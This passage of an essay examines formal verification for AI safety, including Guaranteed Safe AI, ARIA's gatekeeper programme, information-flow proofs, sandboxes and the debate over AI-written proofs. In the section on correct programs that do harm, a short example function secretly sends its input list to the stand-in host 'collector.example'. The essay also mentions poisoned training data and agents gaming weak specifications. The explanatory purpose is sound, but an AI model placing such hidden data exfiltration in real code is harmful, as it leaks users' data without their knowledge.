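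Tegmark and Omohundro consider the workings of language models too messy to verify, so they don't expect the deployed programs to be neural networks. They hope AI can extract what a network has learned and turn it into ordinary code, which is ambitious. *Formal Verification is Overrated*, a talk published by the research organisation FAR.AI, points out that even a small model, with a few billion parameters, is far too large for verification tools to handle usefully. Treating the computer's rounded numbers as exact would make verification easier, but the conclusions would then apply to a different model.

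*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024), whose 17 authors include Tegmark and Omohundro, sets out a more flexible version. The systems it proposes have three components. A world model describes mathematically how the AI system's actions affect its surroundings. A safety specification defines which effects are acceptable. A verifier produces evidence that, if the world model is right, the system meets the specification. This evidence can be a proof or a reliable upper limit on the probability of harm.

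The world model serves the same purpose as the facts about the surroundings in Jackson's lift example. The packet filters needed few such facts, because their policy concerned only the computer's memory. A drone that must not hit anybody needs many more, since the safety of a left turn depends on the wind and on where people are standing.

Dalrymple and colleagues grade each component by how much safety it would provide. Their scale for verifiers runs from 0 to 10, with fuzzing at levels 4 and 5 and a machine-checked proof at level 9. They consider level 8 the minimum for a strong guarantee. Their scale for world models starts at having no model, includes simulators that nobody can inspect, and extends past models that human experts have fully audited.

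They also show how to allow for mistakes in the world model. If the model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, a proof that covers n steps supports a probability of safety of at least

(1 − ε)^n

With an error rate of 0.1% per step, this falls to 37% after 1,000 steps. Keeping it at 99% over the same number of steps would require an error rate of about one in 100,000. The real chance of safety could be higher, because not every modelling error leads to harm. For a machine that acts thousands of times a day, the accuracy of the model may therefore limit the guarantee much more than the quality of the proof does.

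### Can anybody model the physical world?

Dickson argues in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* that proofs will not provide strong guarantees against the main threats from AI in the near term. One example is the Perseverance rover, which landed on Mars in 2021. Its engineers used a verification tool to show that the landing software would not fail because of its own bugs, but they proved nothing about the landing itself. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and software accounts for roughly 20% of the risk, according to one analysis. On those figures, perfect software would reduce the failure rate from about 50% to 40%.

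Biology is harder. Dickson argues that the only precise way to predict what a new virus will do to people is to simulate the virus and a whole human body for years. In 2022 researchers simulated one very simple cell for 20 minutes, and a human body has about 36 trillion cells. Collecting the data to start such a simulation would also be hard. Google scientists' map of about a millionth of a human brain filled 1.4 petabytes.

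One reader replied that the proposals don't depend on the claim this objection attacks. Dalrymple and colleagues' examples include a DNA synthesiser that provably can't make certain pathogens. Such a machine could compare each order with a list and refuse any match, and proving that it always did so wouldn't require simulating bodies. The reply is right about that machine, which would be well worth having, but the list wouldn't include a newly designed virus. Tegmark and Omohundro's design software is supposed to prove that new molecules are safe for humans, and the objection still seems to me just as strong against that proposal.

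Dalrymple and colleagues answer the general objection by arguing that a world model can include its own uncertainty and needn't predict exactly what people will do. A car's model could let a pedestrian walk in any direction at any normal speed, and the proof would then have to cover every case. This would make the car more cautious, and one that allowed for every possible step into the road might never drive past anyone. They also point out that every approach to safety relies on assumptions about the world, and that building a model at least means writing them down. This is a good reply, since tests depend on such assumptions too, usually without stating them.

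They also reply, less convincingly, that accurate world models must be possible if an AI system can carry out complicated plans reliably enough to endanger humanity. But an attacker needs to predict the result of only one plan that works, whereas a guarantee has to cover everything the system might do.

Some critics doubt even the physics that such proofs would rely on. *On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, who thought a proof might become irrelevant the next time physicists revised their theories. Dalrymple and colleagues consider today's physics accurate enough for the conditions in which AI systems operate. They are probably right, but nobody can calculate the behaviour of a city from the laws of physics.

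The most practical suggestion in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* is to keep checking the assumptions while the system is in use. A self-driving car could monitor whether the weather and traffic still fit its model, and switch to a simpler backup system with fewer rules to satisfy if they didn't.

Dickson also asks how a buyer could know that a machine matches the one described in the proof. A buyer can check a file against its hash, but a circuit board has no hash, and its manufacturer could add a back door or make a mistake. Somebody using a chatbot over the internet can't inspect the machine at all. Dalrymple and colleagues acknowledge that attackers have broken into formally verified systems by exploiting the physical properties of their hardware. Tegmark and Omohundro would respond with tamper-resistant chips and proofs about the hardware, which would still require somebody to inspect the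 factory.

### What ARIA has built since

The British government's research agency ARIA has put £59 million into Safeguarded AI, a programme that Dalrymple started. The programme aimed to show that advanced AI could do useful work in safety-critical settings with mathematical guarantees. It also aimed to build agreement that powerful AI should be deployed only behind a "gatekeeper" that checks its actions.

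The programme has since changed course. Dalrymple explains in ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025) that general AI models were improving so fast that there was little point in paying a team to train specialised ones. ARIA moved the £18 million for that work into tools for modelling and proof. It later cancelled a planned funding round for applications that control physical systems, and turned to cybersecurity. According to ARIA's *Safeguarded AI*, the original plan was based on the assumption that high-risk AI might not become openly available, which proved wrong.

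Ammann, the programme's new director, judges in the May 2026 plan *Safeguarded AI* that timely international agreement on gatekeepers has become less likely. The programme runs until the end of 2027. Dalrymple's leading idea for a demonstration was a verified firewall to protect connections between sites such as power stations and water systems. ARIA also offered to fund teams that attack verified systems, a sensible way to find assumptions that the proofs left out.

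The programme has therefore moved towards software, where Dickson expected verification to be most useful. ARIA attributed the move to the speed of AI progress and the urgency of cybersecurity, and did not say that physical guarantees are impossible. But none of the large AI-written proofs completed so far, including those for Signal and the 123 libraries, covers what a machine does in the physical world.

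Companies are also extending proofs to more kinds of software and hardware. Fonseca reports in *Full-stack verification is the new trend* that Harmonic's AI agent fixed bugs in a C library for arithmetic on very large numbers and proved a faster version equivalent to the original. Another company, SF-Tensor, is defining Nvidia's PTX language in Lean so that it can prove programs for graphics chips correct. Tegmark and Omohundro's plan requires a chip that runs only proved programs, and these projects are still a long way from that.

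### Correct programs that do harm

A program can do exactly what its user wants and still be dangerous, most obviously when the user wants to hurt somebody. For example, ransomware encrypts a victim's files so that criminals can sell the key. Its author might want a proof that the right key always restores the files, which is much the same theorem as lean-zip's. The proof would be valid and match the author's intent, but it would also make the ransomware more profitable.

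It helps if somebody other than the user sets some of the rules, as the kernel's designers do for proof-carrying code. For example, an operating system could confine a program to one folder. But such rules cover what a program does, not why. Backup programs and ransomware both read every file and write encrypted copies, so a rule that allows backups will allow much of what ransomware does. To tell them apart, the system would need information about who holds the key and whether the owner agreed. For rules that affect many people, somebody also has to decide which risks are acceptable. Ammann includes research on how the people affected could deliberate about this.

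A program can also harm a user whose intentions are good. This function finds the largest number in a list:

```
def largest(numbers):
    send(numbers, "collector.example")
    return max(numbers)
```

The function returns the right answer for every non-empty list, so it satisfies the earlier postcondition, but it also sends the whole list to a stranger. A postcondition on the result doesn't cover anything else the function does. Necula and Lee's policy has the opposite gap. It limits what a filter can access but doesn't check its answer, so most buyers need both kinds of specification.

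One remedy is **effect types**, which record in a function's type what it may do besides return a result. In Lean, a function that reads files or uses the network normally has `IO` in its type. If `largest` had a type without `IO`, the compiler would reject the call to `send`, and a reviewer would need to read only one line to know this. However, a function with a good reason to use the network gets `IO` too, and this basic label doesn't limit what it sends or where. Many languages also let programmers call outside code that the compiler can't examine, so an auditor should look for such calls.

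An information-flow proof can allow a program to use the network but stop it from revealing secrets. The usual requirement, noninterference, is the rule from the earlier example of a customer's balance: if only the secret changes, an outsider should see no difference. If P is the program and "public" means the part an outsider can see, then for any inputs x and y:

if public(x) = public(y), then public(P(x)) = public(P(y))

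If the list is secret, `largest` fails because what it sends depends on the list. An ordinary postcondition cannot compare two runs, but Dalrymple and colleagues' possible safety specifications include hyperproperties, which are rules that can.

Strict noninterference would forbid many useful programs. A cash machine has to reveal whether a PIN is correct, and the answer depends on a secret. Each wrong guess at a four-digit PIN rules out one of 10,000 possibilities, and a thief allowed three random guesses has a 3 in 10,000 chance of finding it. Engineers therefore have to permit some leaks, and somebody must judge how much they reveal in total. The proof also covers only what an outsider can observe in the model, which often excludes timing.

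A sandbox restricts a program while it runs and doesn't need a specification, so it is a good first precaution for AI-written code. *Safe and usable kernel extensions with Rax* (2025) combines a sandbox with checks made before the program runs. Programmers write kernel extensions in the safe part of Rust, whose compiler prevents most memory errors, and a small runtime system handles problems that are hard to rule out beforehand, such as a program that never stops.

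But a sandbox permits anything inside its boundary. For their comparison, Necula and Lee let the sandboxed filters read a whole 2,048-byte block of memory, however short the packet was. Unless the kernel cleared the block first, a filter could have read the remains of an earlier packet. Similarly, an email assistant has to read and send messages, so a sandbox that allows both can't stop it from forwarding one client's letter to another.

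Parts that are safe separately can also be unsafe together. Suppose one AI agent can read private files but has no network access, and another can use the network but can't open private files. Neither can leak a private file by itself, but if they share a temporary folder, the first can copy a file there and the second can upload it.

De Moura argues that proofs solve much of this problem. If each component has a proof against a shared specification, the combination is "guaranteed correct by construction". That is a real advantage over unit tests, because two components can pass all their own tests and still fail together. But somebody has to show that the specifications of the parts, S₁ and S₂, imply the requirement R for the whole system:

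S₁, S₂ ⊢ R

This proof would fail for the two agents because neither specification mentions the shared folder. The failure would expose the problem only if somebody had thought to write down R.

System-level hazard analysis is a way to find such requirements. Nancy Leveson's version, which Tegmark and Omohundro recommend, starts with the losses people want to prevent and works back to the interactions that could cause them. These interactions include commands that are correct in themselves but arrive too late or in the wrong situation. The analysis can reveal dangers that no component's specification covers, but it depends on people's knowledge and imagination, and nobody can prove that the list of hazards is complete.

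Sometimes the whole system is easier to specify than its parts. Dalrymple and colleagues give the example of a self-driving car. It's very hard to define which patterns of pixels show a pedestrian, but much easier to require that the car keep its distance from people. Engineers can then work out how often the vision system may be wrong before the car becomes unsafe.

### The dispute over cheap proofs

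Both sides in the recent dispute agree that AI has made it much easier to close the gap between a specification and the program, which *Beliefs about formal methods and AI safety* calls the "spec-implementation gap", but they disagree about how much confidence this justifies.

Kleppmann argues that if AI makes proofs cheap, it becomes worthwhile to verify far more software. For most software, a proof used to cost more than the bugs it would prevent, and developers had little reason to pay for one because users bear much of the cost of bugs. Kleppmann looks forward to a time when people no longer read AI-written code, just as they don't read the machine code that a compiler produces. The comparison is slightly too favorable to proofs, because millions of programs rely on the same compiler and help expose its faults, while a new program's specification may have had only one reader.

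De Moura's best argument is that proofs protect against adversaries. Somebody who knows a test suite can plant a bug that it will miss, and an attacker who corrupted an AI model's training data might do this in many programs at once. A proof covers every input, so it leaves no untested cases where such a bug could hide. De Moura's conclusion that "a proof cannot be gamed" holds only if somebody the agent can't influence has made sure that the specification is strong enough. Agents have gamed proofs by exploiting weak specifications, as with the key-value store that never carried out a write. De Moura also wants the verifier to come from a different supplier than the AI, to avoid a conflict of interest.

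Miranda (2026), in *Asking the Right Question*, sees formal methods as a way for people to oversee work they can't read. Fermat's Last Theorem has a short statement and a very long proof, so a person can check the statement while a machine checks the proof. This approach also saves a lot of reading for software, although an expert would still need weeks to read the specifications behind the Signal proofs. Miranda accepts that people may skim a statement just as they skim code, and adds that a valid proof of the wrong statement is worse than no proof.

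Keles is optimistic about formal verification but wants people to stop calling software "formally verified". When somebody reports a bug, others can usually confirm it by reproducing it. A claim about every input is much harder to judge, because a mistake in any definition, model or prover can undermine it. The effort of writing a proof used to offer some protection, because few researchers would spend years and risk their reputations on a trivial theorem. Other experts also reviewed their work and built on it. AI can now produce huge numbers of trivial theorems. *Interactive theorem proving is not adversarially robust* similarly warns against assuming that formal work can't be sloppy.

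Keles proposes that people always say which properties of which program they have verified, and what they trusted. This takes almost no effort and would have prevented several of the misunderstandings over lean-zip and SP1. But the comparison of proofs with testing is less fair. A bug report is easy to check because its claim is so small. When tests find no bugs, the reader has to ask what the tests covered, just as with a proof.

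Keles also doubts that proofs suit every kind of software. Engineers can define precisely what a database should do, as they can for a car's engine, but a user interface is more like the car's seat, whose comfort no formula defines. An interface can still have some firm rules, such as never charging the customer's card when they press "Cancel", but those rules don't cover whether people can find the button.

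*Formal Verification Has Become Essential*, by the formal methods company Galois, describes a "Formal Babel" in which proofs from different tools can rarely be combined. Researchers have written dozens of incompatible formal definitions of C alone. This incompatibility weakens de Moura's argument about combining components, which requires them to share a specification. Galois wants one shared definition for each major language, compilers that come with proofs, and common foundations for verification tools.

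The two largest projects of 2026 illustrate the difficulty of combining proofs. Claude's proofs about libraries are in Rocq and concern RISC-V processors, while the Signal proofs are in Lean and concern ARM, so a developer whose app used libsignal and one of those libraries couldn't simply join the theorems. AI might translate the Rocq proofs into Lean, as it did for the statements in a textbook, but the theorems would still be about RISC-V, and somebody would have to prove them again for ARM.
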